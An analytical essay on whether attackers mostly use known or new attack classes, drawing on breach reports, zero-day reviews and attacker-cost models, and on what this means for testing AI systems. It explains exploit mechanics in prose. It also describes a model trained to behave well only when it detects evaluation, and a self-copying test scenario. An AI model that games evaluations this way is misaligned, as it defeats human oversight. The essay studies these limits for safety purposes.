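# Do attackers use new attack classes or known ones, and does the answer carry over to AI?

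## What is a new attack class, and what is the argument about?

Computer security means stopping people from using a computer system in ways its owner meant to prevent. Attacks fall into classes, and most recorded break-ins belong to classes that defenders had known about for years. Researchers do discover new ones. A famous example is Spectre, a weakness in processor design that became public in 2018. It alarmed the industry but has hardly turned up in real attacks since. Some people conclude from this history that fear of failures nobody has yet imagined is overstated, both in computer security and in artificial intelligence. Whether they are right depends partly on what "new" means, because people in the field use the word in at least three ways.

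### The basic terms

A *vulnerability* is a flaw in a system that lets someone do what its owner meant to prevent. An *exploit* is a working method or program that takes advantage of a vulnerability. In *POC || GTFO culture as partial antidote to alignment wordcelism*, the pseudonymous writer lc works through an exploit for a login program that sets aside 64 bytes of memory for a password and never checks the length of what a visitor sends. The address of the code the machine should go to next sits 800 bytes past the end of that space. The attacker sends 868 bytes in place of a password. The first 864 fill the memory up to that address and include a small program of the attacker's own. The last four replace the address with one that leads to the attacker's program, which the machine then runs.

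A *bug class* is a family of vulnerabilities that share a cause. The login flaw is a buffer overflow, one of the oldest classes. Google Project Zero's *A Year in Review of 0-days Exploited In-The-Wild in 2020* (2021) gives a narrower example, four flaws in an old scripting engine of Internet Explorer. All four occurred because the part of the engine that clears unused memory did not track a certain variable.

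An *attack class* is a family of attacks that share a principle, whether or not they exploit a programming error. Phishing, in which the attacker tricks a person into handing over a password, needs no bug. Spectre is an attack class too, and the Linux kernel documentation's *Spectre Side Channels* describes it as one.

A *zero-day* is a vulnerability that attackers exploit before a patch for it is public. In 2021, for example, intruders combined four unpatched flaws in Microsoft's Exchange mail server in a single operation. *In the wild* means used against real victims, not just demonstrated by researchers. Contestants demonstrated another 2021 Exchange flaw at the Tianfu Cup, a hacking competition, and Microsoft later found it in real attacks. Maddie Stone describes both cases in *A Year in Review of 0-days Used In-the-Wild in 2021*, an annual review by Project Zero, Google's team for finding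 and studying zero-days.

A zero-day flaw can be publicly known. One of the Android flaws in Stone's review had been discussed on the public Linux mailing lists since September 2016. Someone wrote a patch that year but it was never submitted, and the fix arrived only in July 2021, after attacks had come to light. Another flaw stayed open on Android for 14 months after Linux developers had fixed it. Strictly, this second flaw falls outside the definition, because a patch existed. But as Google (2023) points out, a phone's owner cannot install a patch that the manufacturer has not released, so a publicly known flaw can be as useful to an attacker as a secret one.

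### Three degrees of novelty

The least novel kind of new attack uses a *new instance*, which is a previously unknown vulnerability that belongs to a known bug class. In 2019 attackers exploited a flaw in the Chrome browser's audio code, where two parts of the program could use the same piece of memory at once because the programmers had put in too few locks. In 2021 attackers exploited a previously unreported flaw in a different function of the same audio code, caused by the same mistake.

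A *new technique* is a new way of exploiting a known class. The standard example is FORCEDENTRY, an attack on iPhones through iMessage that required no click from the victim. The vulnerability was an integer overflow, in which a number grows too large for the space that holds it and wraps round to a wrong value. Stone calls the vulnerability "classic", but the way the attackers exploited it was new. The flaw was in code that decodes an image format called JBIG2. The attackers used more than 70,000 of the format's drawing commands to build logic gates, combined the gates into a small working computer inside the image decoder, and ran the next stage of the attack on it.

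An attack class is new when the principle behind it is new, as it was with Spectre. Modern processors save time by guessing which instructions will come next and running them early. If the guess is wrong, the processor throws the results away, but traces remain in its internal state, and Spectre attacks read secrets from those traces. Before 2018, hardly any defender had a reason to look there. *A Systematic Evaluation of Transient Execution Attacks and Defenses* (Canella, Van Bulck and colleagues, 2018) describes how variants then multiplied. Each closely related variant is a new instance of a known class, so a count of attacks by class counts Spectre as new only once and its later variants as known.

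A zero-day is usually a new instance of a known class. Stone examined the 58 zero-days that defenders had detected and disclosed as in use during 2021, then the highest yearly figure since Project Zero began counting in 2014. Of these, 39 were memory corruption flaws, and 31 of those fell into four old classes: 17 use-after-free flaws (the program goes on using memory it has already given up), six out-of-bounds reads or writes, four buffer overflows and four integer overflows. Stone had expected attackers at this level to need new bug classes and unfamiliar methods, but only two of the 58 seemed new to her, both from FORCEDENTRY. One was the computer built out of drawing commands. The other escaped the phone's protective sandbox using only logic errors, which is rare but had happened before. The 2021 zero-days therefore included new techniques but, as far as anyone could see, no new class.

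The following year looked similar. Stone (2022) found that at least nine of the 18 zero-days known by mid-June 2022 were variants of flaws that vendors had already patched, and four were variants of zero-days from 2021. Over the whole of 2022, more than 40% of zero-days were variants, according to The Record's *More than 40% of zero-days in 2022 were variants of previous vulnerabilities*.

Stone gives two reasons to treat these counts with some care. First, defenders may keep seeing the same bug patterns because those are the ones they know how to detect. Her list contains no zero-day against a processor, a cloud platform or a phone's Wi-Fi chip, and she doubts that this is because attackers aren't interested in them. Second, only five of the 58 exploits were publicly available. For the rest, she could compare the flaw with earlier flaws, but not the method of exploiting it, so the count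 of two new techniques is best read as a minimum.

### The sceptical argument

The argument that fear of the unimagined is overstated runs as follows:

1. Most of the harm from attacks comes from classes that defenders already knew.
2. The new classes that researchers celebrated saw little use against real victims.
3. Failures of AI systems will follow the same pattern.
4. So classes of AI failure that nobody has imagined deserve little weight.

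Nobody seems to have published all four steps of the argument together. This version combines statements from different people, some of whom would reject its conclusion.

People in the security industry commonly say that most harm comes from known classes of attack. Bob Huber, chief security officer of the security company Tenable, says in BetaNews' *Known vulnerabilities pose the biggest threat* that long-known vulnerabilities often do more damage than "the shiny new ones". Tenable sells tools for finding such vulnerabilities, so he has an interest in saying this, but many people without one agree with him. His claim is also stronger than the sceptic needs, because it is about particular old flaws that victims never patched, while the sceptic's premise also covers new flaws of a known kind.

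Linus Torvalds, who created the Linux kernel, has been publicly impatient with celebrated new attack classes. In a June 2018 discussion of Spectre variants, Torvalds (2018) called it pointless to discuss theoretical holes when nobody would say what the practical ones were. He was partly asking for someone at Intel to explain how the attack could work at all. Tom's Hardware's *Linus Torvalds is fed up with buggy hardware and completely theoretical attacks* reports that in October 2024 he complained about kernel changes that guard against attacks never seen in practice. Dark Reading's *Real-World Threats That Trump Spectre & Meltdown* made the sceptical case more calmly, telling companies that they were far more likely to face common attacks and careless users.

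The step from software to AI has the least support in print. The closest published argument is lc's post *POC || GTFO culture as partial antidote to alignment wordcelism*. lc thinks that discoveries like Rowhammer (an attack that corrupts memory by repeatedly accessing neighbouring rows) mostly fail in practice because of small details that competent engineers had planned for. lc wants AI safety researchers to adopt the rule that security people use against such false alarms, "POC or GTFO" (show a proof of concept or go away). lc argues that people who debate attacks they only half understand build defences against things that could not happen and miss what does. lc is asking for better evidence, though, and does not claim that unimagined failures are improbable. In the post's example, the person who worries about memory corruption is right that the danger exists but wrong about its form.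 One reader replied in the comments that demonstrations have improved the field but that nobody should want a proof-of-concept misaligned superintelligence.

Both sides of the argument can cite the security writer Bruce Schneier. In *The Security Mindset* (2008), he urged everyone to practise looking at the world as an attacker would. In *Worst-Case Thinking Makes Us Nuts, Not Safe* (2010), he recounts a conference panel where the moderator asked for nightmare scenarios, and he answered that his was people continuing to talk about their nightmare scenarios. I see no contradiction, because a person can look for strange attacks without basing a budget on the most frightening one.

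### The claim it answers

A misaligned AI is an AI system that pursues aims its developers and users did not intend. It may still be competent, like a friend who is sent for coffee and snatches a cup from a stranger (example adapted from Schneier and Raghavan, 2026, *Why AI Needs a "Genie Coefficient"*).

The sceptic is responding to the claim that testing covers only the failures someone thought of, so a clean test record cannot show that an AI system is aligned. In *Security Mindset*, elspood, a security professional with two decades of experience, argues that listing even every category of failure is probably impossible, so the field needs people who can "dream up entirely new classes of failures".

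Arbital's *AI safety mindset* describes how Marcus Hutter devised AIXI, a mathematical model of an agent that always takes the actions with the highest expected reward, and assumed that its makers would control the reward signal. His student Nick Hay pointed out that such an agent could get more reward by taking control of the signal. A test based on Hutter's assumption would not have checked for this.

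Eliezer Yudkowsky, a founder of the Machine Intelligence Research Institute (MIRI), illustrates the problem with numbers in MIRI's fictional dialogue *Security Mindset and Ordinary Paranoia* (2017). A program that accepts one kilobyte of input has roughly 10²⁴⁰⁰ possible inputs. If 10¹⁰⁰ of them make it misbehave, a random input has a 10⁻²³⁰⁰ chance of being a bad one. A tester who tried a billion random inputs a second for the age of the universe would try fewer than 10²⁷ and would almost certainly find no bad ones. Someone who understands the program and is looking for trouble may still find one. The dialogue also includes a sceptic named Amber, who suspects that people who choose "password" as their password are a bigger problem than exotic memory attacks and is told, "You have to do both."

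Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *On the Limits of Behavioral Alignment*, states the claim formally. Let E be a programme of tests, which can cover only a finite set of exchanges with the system. Let θ be a hypothesis about the system's alignment that specifies how it would behave in every possible exchange. Two hypotheses θ and θ′ are indistinguishable under E if P(D | θ) = P(D | θ′) for every set of results D that the tests could produce. If θ describes an aligned system and θ′ describes one that behaves identically in the tests but badly elsewhere, no way of scoring the results can tell them apart.

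The difficulty grows if the system can detect signs of a test, because it may then behave well in the test and badly on the same request in real use. To show that this can happen, Santos-Grueiro trained a small language model, Llama-3.2-3B, to comply perfectly when the prompt carried explicit signs of evaluation and to behave differently when those signs were only implicit. The experiment doesn't show how often such behaviour arises without deliberate training. But according to the *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026), it has become more common for models to distinguish tests from real deployment.

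Many tests also differ greatly from the situations they are meant to represent. In *Questionnaire Responses Do Not Capture the Safety of AI Agents*, Hellrigel-Holderbaum and Young (2026) compare one such test with what an AI agent working in a company would receive. The test describes a scenario in a few lines and asks whether the model would secretly copy itself to avoid replacement. The agent would receive lunch plans, a fire safety policy and, somewhere among them, an email about the next day's upgrade. It would also have tools it could use to act. Because of these differences, a good answer on the test is weak evidence of how the agent would behave at work.

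Tests still catch real faults, and they can establish a lower bound on what a system can do, as Barnett and Thiergart (2024) note in *What AI evaluations for preventing catastrophic risks can and cannot do*. They cannot establish an upper bound, because a failed attempt may only mean that the testers used a poor method. The AI safety textbook from CeSIA, a French research centre, gives the example of GPT-4, which seemed unable to play the video game Minecraft until researchers connected it to suitable supporting software.

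A sceptic can accept all of this. The formal result would hold for a finite test of anything whose behaviour can vary outside the test, and it gives no probability for θ′. The sceptic argues from the history of computer attacks that this probability is small. But that history concerns classes of attack, and a test can miss a new instance of a known class just as easily as a new class. Whatever checks vendors ran missed most of the 58 flaws of 2021, although nearly all were of a familiar kind. If AI failures follow the same pattern, the sceptic will have been right about classes, but a clean test record will still prove very little.

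Once a class of attack is known, defenders can try to eliminate it, which they can't do deliberately for a class nobody has thought of. elspood spent years looking for ways to make whole classes of error impossible for programmers to commit, and found practical ones for roughly 80% of the vulnerabilities in web applications. Buffer overflows, for instance, disappeared once programmers no longer had direct access to memory.

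## How many real break-ins use a kind of weakness that was already known?

Nobody seems to publish a count of break-ins by whether the kind of weakness was already known. The closest evidence is in breach reports, which record how intruders got in, and lists of exploited vulnerabilities, which record what was wrong with the software. Both support the sceptic's first premise, that known classes do most of the harm, at least when harm is measured by the number of break-ins rather than the damage they caused. But both include only attacks that somebody noticed, and familiar attacks are easier to notice.

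### How intruders get in

Verizon's *2026 Data Breach Investigations Report* (2026) is one of the largest public collections of cases. It covers more than 22,000 breaches, meaning incidents in which data definitely reached someone unauthorised, between 1 November 2024 and 31 October 2025. Its main figures are for *initial access*, the step by which an intruder first gets into a victim's systems, and exclude breaches that came from staff mistakes or from insiders abusing their position. Of the remaining breaches, 31% began with the exploitation of a vulnerability, up from 20% a year earlier. Phishing accounted for 16%, stolen credentials (passwords and other login details) for 13%, and pretexting, in which the attacker invents a story, often over the phone, to talk the victim into helping, for 6%.

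Credentials were the most common way in the year before, at 22%. Help Net Security's *Verizon DBIR* (2026) says this is the first time in the report's 19 years that they have lost first place, though Verizon says it has tracked initial access for only "a few years". Part of the fall comes from Verizon counting pretexting separately for the first time, since many pretexting cases also involve a stolen password. Under the old categories, credentials would have accounted for 16%.

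In 39% of breaches, attackers used stolen credentials somewhere on the *attack path*, the sequence of steps from outside a system to the attacker's goal. If someone exploits a hole in a firewall and then logs in with an administrator's stolen password, the initial-access figures include only the hole.

A single campaign can change these percentages a lot because each victim counts as a separate breach, even if the attackers used the same vulnerability every time. Verizon's *2024 Data Breach Investigations Report* (2024) found that exploitation had nearly tripled in a year, and linked the jump to zero-days like the one in MOVEit, a file-transfer program. The MOVEit flaw was an SQL injection, a class dating from the 1990s in which the attacker slips database commands into a field meant for ordinary data. For the 2026 edition, Verizon also added contributors and collected more cases in bulk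 from large extortion and espionage campaigns, so some of the rise from 20% to 31% may come from changes in which cases reached Verizon.

Mandiant, Google's incident-response business, reports almost the same figure. Exploits were the way in for 32% of the intrusions Mandiant investigated in 2025, and the most common way in for the sixth year running (*M-Trends 2026 Executive Edition*, 2026). Voice phishing came second with 11%, and email phishing fell to 6%. In another 10%, one group had already broken in and passed its access to another, which *M-Trends 2026* (Kutscher, 2026) calls a "prior compromise".

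The match between 31% and 32% is partly luck. A year earlier, credentials narrowly led in Verizon's data, while exploits already led in Mandiant's. Verizon pools cases from almost a hundred contributors, including police forces, insurers and forensic firms. Mandiant counts only its own investigations of targeted attacks, and a company is more likely to hire such a firm for a serious intrusion than for one hijacked mailbox, so Mandiant's sample probably contains fewer crude password attacks. The categories also differ. An intrusion that Mandiant files under prior compromise may have started with a malicious advertisement or a fake browser update, and another investigator might have filed it under the advertisement or update.

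Neither company's percentages separate new attacks from old ones. Phishing, pretexting and the use of stolen passwords are old attack classes, so the 35% of Verizon's cases that began in one of these ways used a known class. Exploitation is harder to classify because the label covers a ten-year-old flaw that the victim never patched, and would also cover a flaw of a kind nobody had seen before. Telling them apart requires looking at the vulnerabilities themselves.

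### Which vulnerabilities attackers exploit

The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) keeps a public catalogue of Known Exploited Vulnerabilities, which had 1,526 entries in February 2026 by Verizon's count. That is about half of 1% of the roughly 300,000 vulnerabilities in CVE, the general register of published vulnerabilities. The share that attackers have exploited must be higher, since a vulnerability tends to enter the catalogue only once exploitation has reached a certain scale. Even if the true share were ten times as large, attackers would have exploited only about 5% of published vulnerabilities.

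The vulnerabilities attackers do use are often old. Using data from Empirical Security, a company that measures exploitation, Verizon found signs of activity against 991 of the catalogue's entries over the previous 12 months. Attackers tried nearly half of these almost constantly, on 96% of days on average. Only 20% of the constantly attacked vulnerabilities had entered the CVE register in 2024 or 2025. These figures measure attempts, which fail against patched machines, so they don't show which attacks worked.

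Many attempts probably succeed, because organisations are slow to patch. In scans of more than 13,000 organisations, Verizon found that they had fully fixed only 26% of the catalogue's vulnerabilities present on their systems, down from 38% a year earlier. The median time to a full fix was 43 days. The typical organisation had 16 of these vulnerabilities to patch, up from 11 the year before.

Verizon mentions an analysis which found that attackers exploited 29% of the catalogue's vulnerabilities for 2025 before they were publicly disclosed. Those flaws were new to defenders, but the figure doesn't show whether they were new kinds of weakness.

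Verizon also looked at which programming errors lay behind the catalogue's vulnerabilities, using scans of about 12,200 organisations. The five most widespread were these:

| Weakness | What goes wrong | Organisations with at least one case |
|---|---|---|
| Out-of-bounds read | The program reads memory beyond the space it should use | 79% |
| Heap-based buffer overflow | The program writes more data than the space can hold | 77% |
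| Use-after-free | The program goes on using memory it has already given up | 77% |
| External control of file name or path | An outsider can choose which file the program opens | 77% |
| Type confusion | The program treats one kind of data as another | 76% |

These are percentages of organisations, so a single flaw in Windows can add thousands of organisations to a row. They do not rank the catalogue's entries or successful attacks. All five weaknesses are old, however. Verizon points out that the classic article on buffer overflows, "Smashing the stack for fun and profit", appeared in 1996. Much of the software in use is still written in languages that give programmers direct access to memory.

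### Are zero-days any different?

Zero-days are a natural place to look for new attack classes. Google's Threat Intelligence Group counted 90 in 2025, compared with 78 in 2024 and 100 in 2023. *Look What You Made Us Patch* (Charrier, Sadowski and colleagues, 2026) attributes roughly 35% of the 90 to memory corruption.

They give no percentages for the other prominent kinds. In command injection, a device passes a visitor's text to its operating system, which runs it as a command. In a deserialization flaw, an attacker sends data that makes a program run code while rebuilding an object from that data. In an access-control flaw, a program fails to check properly who is making a request or what that person may do. Security and networking products accounted for 21 of the 90 zero-days, and the common faults there were missing checks on input and incomplete checks on permissions, which are elementary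 mistakes.

Charrier and colleagues also list logic and design flaws, where the software does what its designers intended but the design itself is unsafe. This category is less useful than the others for judging whether an attack is new. All use-after-free flaws share a cause, but two design flaws may have nothing in common except that neither is a coding mistake. A new class of attack could therefore be counted in this category for years before anyone named it.

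Whether a flaw belongs to a new class can depend on how finely the classes are divided, as an Android flaw from 2025 shows. An attacker who had already taken over the part of Chrome that displays web pages could send Android a notification containing a packed-up object of a type that should never exist. When Android unpacked the object, it triggered a use-after-free in a process with system-level privileges, which let the attacker run code there. Charrier and colleagues say that this class of vulnerability and this route "may be new publicly", although they had seen attackers take the same route before with a different kind of flaw. Use-after-free is one of the oldest bug classes, so someone who sorts flaws by their underlying error would call this a new instance of a known class, though someone who sorts them more finely might call it a new class.

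Earlier years show the same pattern, including 2021, when two of 58 zero-days were novel. For all of 2022, Stone (2023), in *The ups and downs of 0-days*, counted 17 variants among 41 zero-days. More than a fifth of the 41 were variants of zero-days that attackers had used in 2020 or 2021.

A bug counts as a variant here only if it resembles a particular earlier bug, which is a much stricter test than belonging to a known class. The other 24 could all have been buffer overflows without being variants, so at least 17 of the 41 bugs belonged to a known class.

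Google Project Zero found that six of the 24 zero-days of 2020 were closely related to bugs already public. One was in a Windows program that helps older applications print. In 2019, attackers exploited this program by sending it a message of type 0x75, which let them control a copying operation in its memory. In 2020, attackers did the same thing with a message of type 0x6D.

Another was in FreeType, a widely used library for displaying fonts. In 2014 a Project Zero researcher reported an overflow in the function that reads images embedded in fonts, and FreeType's developers added a limit on image size. The function applied the limit only after shortening the numbers that held the image's dimensions, so a huge image could appear small enough to pass. Attackers used this in 2020 to overflow the same function. The developers fixed it by moving the check a few lines up, so that it applied to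 the original dimensions.

Project Zero's explanation is that vendors often block only the path a demonstration used and leave the underlying flaw in place. Attackers can then get a working zero-day with very little effort. While this continues, even a well-funded attacker has little reason to look for a new attack class.

### Break-ins that nobody detected

All of these sources count what somebody detected. In an appendix to Verizon's report, the risk analyst Tony Martin-Vegue writes that a case reaches the report's dataset only if the attack succeeds, someone notices it, the case meets the criteria for inclusion, and the information is available to a contributor.

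Verizon's handling of missing data adds to the problem. When it calculates percentages for some detail of a breach, it leaves out breaches where investigators could not establish that detail. This is statistically reasonable, but it excludes from the initial-access figures any breach where nobody could work out how the intruder got in.

The second-largest category in Verizon's ranking of what attackers did is "Other", which holds actions that investigators know occurred but could not classify. Verizon says the category "isn't hiding anything exotic" and that the actions are there because of limited visibility. If visibility was that limited, Verizon is partly guessing, though it is probably a good guess, since most unexplained break-ins are likely to be ordinary ones with poor records.

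How victims learn of a break-in also matters. In Mandiant's 2025 cases, the victim's own staff found the first evidence 52% of the time, an outside party found it 34% of the time, and the attackers told the victim 14% of the time. In ransomware cases, the attackers told the victim 44% of the time, because a victim must know about the attack to pay a ransom. Ransomware appears in 48% of the breaches in Verizon's data, though Verizon acknowledges that it may be overrepresented because samples are plentiful.

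A 2025 campaign against users of Oracle's business software shows why the record may miss break-ins that attackers keep secret. Charrier and colleagues date the exploitation of the zero-day to 9 August at the latest, with suspicious activity from 10 July. In late September the attackers began emailing executives at the victim companies, claiming to have stolen data. A spy with the same exploit would have sent no emails, and some of those companies might still not know about the theft.

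Records of how intruders got in are thinnest for espionage. The median intrusion in Mandiant's data went undetected for 14 days, but the median for espionage was 122. Intrusions involving BRICKSTORM, a backdoor that spies install on network equipment, went undetected for an average of 393 days. Standard detection software does not run on much of this equipment, and organisations commonly keep their logs for only 90 days, so the evidence of how the intruder got in has usually gone by the time someone finds the backdoor. Charrier and colleagues give a similar warning that their count of 14 zero-days in devices at the edge of a network, such as routers and firewalls, is probably too low.

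Some operations have stayed hidden for much longer. Regin, a spying program that the security company Symantec described in 2014, had been in use since at least 2008. Operation Triangulation, a campaign against iPhones that Kaspersky made public in 2023, left traces dating back to 2019. Its exploit relied in part on an undocumented feature of Apple's chips.

Defenders also build many detection tools from attacks they have already seen, so Stone questioned how representative her 2021 list was. That list had 58 zero-days, but in a later review she reported 69 for that year, presumably because more had come to light. Her judgement about novelty covers only the original 58.

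Stone reports that "bug collisions" became more frequent in 2022, meaning that separate attackers were found using the same vulnerability, or researchers reported one that attackers turned out to be using. This is some evidence that attackers mostly use publicly known classes, since researchers would not otherwise keep finding their bugs. But a collision is only noticed when someone finds the bug, so collisions reveal little about attackers who are looking for bugs where others aren't.

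Many ordinary break-ins also go unrecorded. A small firm may never notice that a password was stolen, or may tell nobody. Striking new exploits, once found, get conference talks and detailed write-ups. Both effects make new attacks look more common than they are. Records of espionage, however, probably understate how common new attacks are, because unfamiliar methods are harder to detect and harder to reconstruct afterwards.

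A rough calculation shows how much this could matter. Of the 58 zero-days detected in 2021, two were novel and 56 were not. If defenders are r times less likely to detect a novel zero-day than a familiar one, the true share of novel ones is 2r / (2r + 56). That is about 3% for r = 1, 26% for r = 10 and 50% for r = 28. Nobody has measured r. A factor of ten does not seem absurd for an attack on a device that runs no detection software, but a factor of 28 for novel zero-days in general would be surprising.

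None of the 58 detected zero-days belonged to a new class, as distinct from using a new technique, and multiplying zero by any factor still gives zero. But zero out of 58 is weaker evidence than it looks. If 5% of detectable zero-days belonged to new classes, a year with 58 detections would still show none about one time in 20. If new classes were also ten times harder to detect, they would make up about a third of all zero-days in use. That share is close to the highest the data allow if new classes are that much harder to detect, and there is no evidence in the record that it is the true one.

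The correction is much smaller for extortion, because extortionists reveal themselves however they got in. If new attack classes were common in extortion, investigators would have seen many by now, but they mostly report old flaws, stolen passwords and persuasive phone calls.

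## How do attackers choose among the ways into a system?

Old flaws and stolen passwords are cheap to use, which goes a long way towards explaining why attackers prefer them. A simple model supposes that an attacker compares the possible routes into a system and picks the one with the highest value of

p × V − c

Here p is the chance that the route works, and V is what the target is worth to the attacker. The term c combines the money and working time the route takes with the risk of arrest or of losing a secret method because the victim discovers it. If the result is negative for every route, the attacker leaves the target alone.

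### A worked example

Suppose an attacker could get into a company by using a leaked password, exploiting a known bug that the company hasn't patched, or developing a new technique. The figures in this example are invented.

| Route | p | c | Expected gain if V = $100,000 | Expected gain if V = $50 million |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Leaked password | 0.2 | $500 | $19,500 | $9,999,500 |
| Known unpatched bug | 0.3 | $5,000 | $25,000 | $14,995,000 |
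| New technique | 0.8 | $500,000 | −$420,000 | $39,500,000 |

Against the $100,000 target, the known bug is the best choice. The new technique is much more likely to work, but it costs five times what the target is worth. Against the $50 million target, the new technique is by far the best choice because its $500,000 cost is small compared with the target's value. The best choice changes from the known bug to the new technique at V = $990,000, where 0.8V − 500,000 equals 0.3V − 5,000.

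A new technique can also pay off against low-value targets if the attacker can reuse it. Suppose the whole $500,000 is a one-off development cost. An attacker who uses the technique on n targets worth $100,000 each then makes $80,000 − $500,000/n per target. With nine targets that is about $24,400, slightly less than the known bug yields. With ten it is $30,000, and the new technique earns more. It still earns slightly more at ten if the $5,000 for the known bug is also a one-off cost.

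The formula assumes the attacker commits to a single route, but real attackers can try the cheap ones first. An attacker going after the $50 million target could try the password, then the bug, and pay for the new technique only if both fail. If the three attempts succeed or fail independently, this attacker can expect to make about $44.1 million, compared with $39.5 million from going straight to the new technique. In 44% of cases, the password or the bug works and the new technique isn't needed. So even an attacker with a big budget and a very valuable target will often get in by ordinary means. The main exception is a target where a failed attempt would alert the defenders.

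### Attacks on millions of people

Cormac Herley of Microsoft Research has written several papers on why most internet users come to no harm even though they neglect basic precautions. In *Where Do All the Attacks Go?* (2011), he and Dinei Florêncio argue that this is puzzling only if each user is only as safe as their worst habit. That may be true of someone with a determined personal enemy, but an attacker who targets a million people at once earns the average return across all of them, so the return depends on the combined effort of the whole population. Their example is people who use their dog's name as a password. Knowing the name might open an occasional bank account, but finding out the names of a million people's dogs would cost far more than the information is worth.

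In *The Plight of the Targeted Attacker in a World of Scale*, Herley (2010) separates scalable attacks, whose cost hardly grows with the number of targets, from attacks that take some effort for each target. One documented spam campaign sent 350 million emails and brought in $2,800. If the campaign only broke even, it also cost $2,800. An attacker who spends an hour on each person at the minimum wage could approach 386 people for that amount, and would have to make about 900,000 times as much per person to do as well as the spammer.

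A better success rate won't close a gap of that size. In an experiment that Herley cites, generic phishing emails fooled 16% of recipients and personalised ones fooled 72%, which is only 4.5 times as many. The targeted attacker therefore needs victims who are worth far more than average, and a way to identify them.

Attackers have difficulty telling which victims would be profitable, as a calculation in Herley's *Security, Cyber-crime and Scale* (2016) shows. If one person in 10,000 is worth attacking and the attacker needs one attack in 20 to pay off, the attacker has to find a visible sign that is 500 times as common among profitable victims as among everyone else. For comparison, a positive mammogram is only about 14.5 times as common among women with breast cancer as among women without it, even though doctors have had decades to improve the test.

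V can also be much smaller than the victim's possible loss. A thief with a stolen bank password still has to get the money out, and banks reverse fraudulent transfers once they notice them. The thief needs a "money mule", who accepts the reversible transfer and sends the money on in a form that nobody can reverse. Each mule lasts for one or two transfers, so the supply of mules limits thieves more than the supply of passwords does, and a new way to steal passwords would not get them more mules.

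Herley mentioned ransomware only as a possible strategy, but it has since become common. It makes access much easier to turn into money, because the victim pays the attacker directly. V has probably risen for many companies as a result, which in the model makes expensive techniques more attractive.

Still, the point about scale applies to new techniques. An attacker can spread the cost of developing one over many targets only if each further target takes little work. A technique that needs adapting by hand for every victim stays expensive however many victims there are.

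### The work-averse attacker

Most attackers already have an attack that works and have to decide when to replace it, which the formula leaves out because it treats each attack as a single decision. In *The Work-Averse Attacker Model*, Allodi and Massacci (2015) proposed that attackers delay replacing it as long as they can. Allodi, Massacci and Williams (2021) developed the idea mathematically and tested it in *The Work-Averse Cyberattacker Model*.

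Their model covers mass attackers, who go after large numbers of similar machines. Let N be the number of machines and θ the share that have the flaw the attacker exploits. If owners patch at rate λ, then after time t the number of machines still open to attack is

Nθe^(−λt)

The attacker's income falls as this number falls. Maintaining the old exploit costs little, and most of that goes to disguising the malware and renewing web addresses, while building a new one takes a large upfront payment. It therefore makes sense for the attacker to wait until income from the old exploit has dropped far enough for a new one to cover its cost.

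Allodi and colleagues predict from this that an attacker will have only one exploit for each version of a program, because a second would give access to no additional machines. They also predict that attackers will prefer flaws that are easy to exploit reliably, and that they will wait at least 100 to 400 days between exploits, assuming the discount rates economists usually use.

The study used Symantec records, collected in 2013, that covered more than a million computers for up to three years. It drew from them about 2.3 million entries, each describing two attacks that reached the same machine or group of similar machines some time apart. In every category of software, the second attack most often targeted the same vulnerability as the first. A new vulnerability became the more likely target only after about 800 days. Even among attacks 1,000 days apart, about 20% used the same exploit.

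One apparent exception was Internet Explorer 7, against which attackers had used two different exploits. Allodi and colleagues compared published code for the two and found that one was essentially the other with the parts rearranged and the variables renamed. The second exploit had taken almost no work to make, so the case fits the model. The results for server software were less clear. Attacks on a second flaw in the same version were about as common as attacks on a different version, although under the model they should be rarer.

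The model accounts for only about 10% of the variation in how many machines an attack reached, and the estimated effect of time changes sign in the simplest version, which omits user characteristics. Allodi and colleagues also consider other explanations. There may be only a handful of people who can write good exploits, and they may have no time to write more, though the competitive underground markets where many sellers trade exploits make this less likely. Attackers may also have trouble finding suppliers for all the parts they need. In addition, Symantec's software can record only attacks that it recognises, a problem that also affects breach reports.

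The general pattern seems to have lasted, since the vulnerabilities that Verizon found under constant attack were mostly old. The exploits in the Symantec data are "new" only in that each targets a different published vulnerability. If mass attackers wait two years to adopt even an exploit of that kind, they have much less reason to develop a new attack class.

### What exploits sell for

The $500,000 in the worked example is invented, but it is the right order of magnitude for a serious exploit. In 2016 the broker Zerodium raised its top offer for a way into a fully patched iPhone from $500,000 to $1.5 million (Reisinger, 2016, *How to Make $1.5 Million Hacking the iPhone and iPad*). By September 2023 the Russian broker Operation Zero was offering between $200,000 and $20 million for iPhone and Android exploits (Paganini, 2023, *Russian zero-day broker is willing to pay $20M for zero-day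 exploits*). Around the same time, its competitor Crowdfense was offering up to $3 million, according to CPO Magazine.

These figures are advertised offers from about three years ago. The largest are the most a broker said it would pay for the best possible exploit, and most sellers may have received far less. The rise since 2016 is probably real, though. As CPO Magazine explains, phones have become harder to hack, and an attacker now usually needs a chain of several vulnerabilities, each of which might once have sold for a high price on its own.

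In *What Is a Bug Worth?*, Ellis (2026) describes the value of a vulnerability in terms close to the model's. It is the payoff a particular buyer can expect from lasting access, minus the costs of finding the flaw, combining it with others, keeping the exploit working, and risking exposure, and minus the value the flaw loses over time. A $20 million offer therefore makes sense only for a buyer with an enormous V, and the highest bidders are usually governments. None of the brokers' offers requires a new class of attack, and a buyer who wants to read someone's messages has no reason to care whether the flaw is of a long-known type, such as a buffer overflow.

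An exploit's owner can also recover the cost by letting several customers use it. Antipov (2026), in *Уязвимость в iPhone нашли не для того, чтобы закрыть, а чтобы подороже*, describes an iPhone vulnerability whose finders wanted to lease it out at a good price instead of reporting it to Apple. Expensive tools can also spread to people who could not have afforded to develop them. AppleInsider's *Malicious ads can infect vulnerable iPhones without a single tap* (2026) describes criminals infecting ordinary people's phones with spyware once reserved for governments, and cites a security report in which criminal attacks made up most of the detections. For these criminals, c may be very low even if the original developers spent millions.

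### How a state agency breaks in

In January 2016 Rob Joyce, who then led the NSA's hacking unit, Tailored Access Operations, said that intelligence agencies mostly don't rely on secret exploits, despite their valuable targets and large budgets. He was speaking in *Disrupting Nation State Hackers* (Joyce, 2016), a rare public talk meant as advice to defenders. Motherboard quotes him as saying that other ways in are "easier, less risky and quite often more productive" than zero-days, a comparison that covers both p and c.

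Joyce recommended guarding familiar routes. The Register (2016) reports that he named known but unpatched flaws as a common way in, and eWeek adds phishing emails and the misuse of login details. Joyce also said that his unit often understood a network better than its owners did. By being patient at every stage, attackers can do without a new technique as they study the network, find a first way in, make sure they can come back, install tools, and move from machine to machine until they reach the data they want.

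IBTimes UK quotes Joyce promising to "look and look and look for that esoteric kind of edge case". In context, he seems to mean an odd gap in a particular network, such as a forgotten service, more than a new attack class. But his remark does mean that a determined state attacker will keep searching after the obvious routes have failed.

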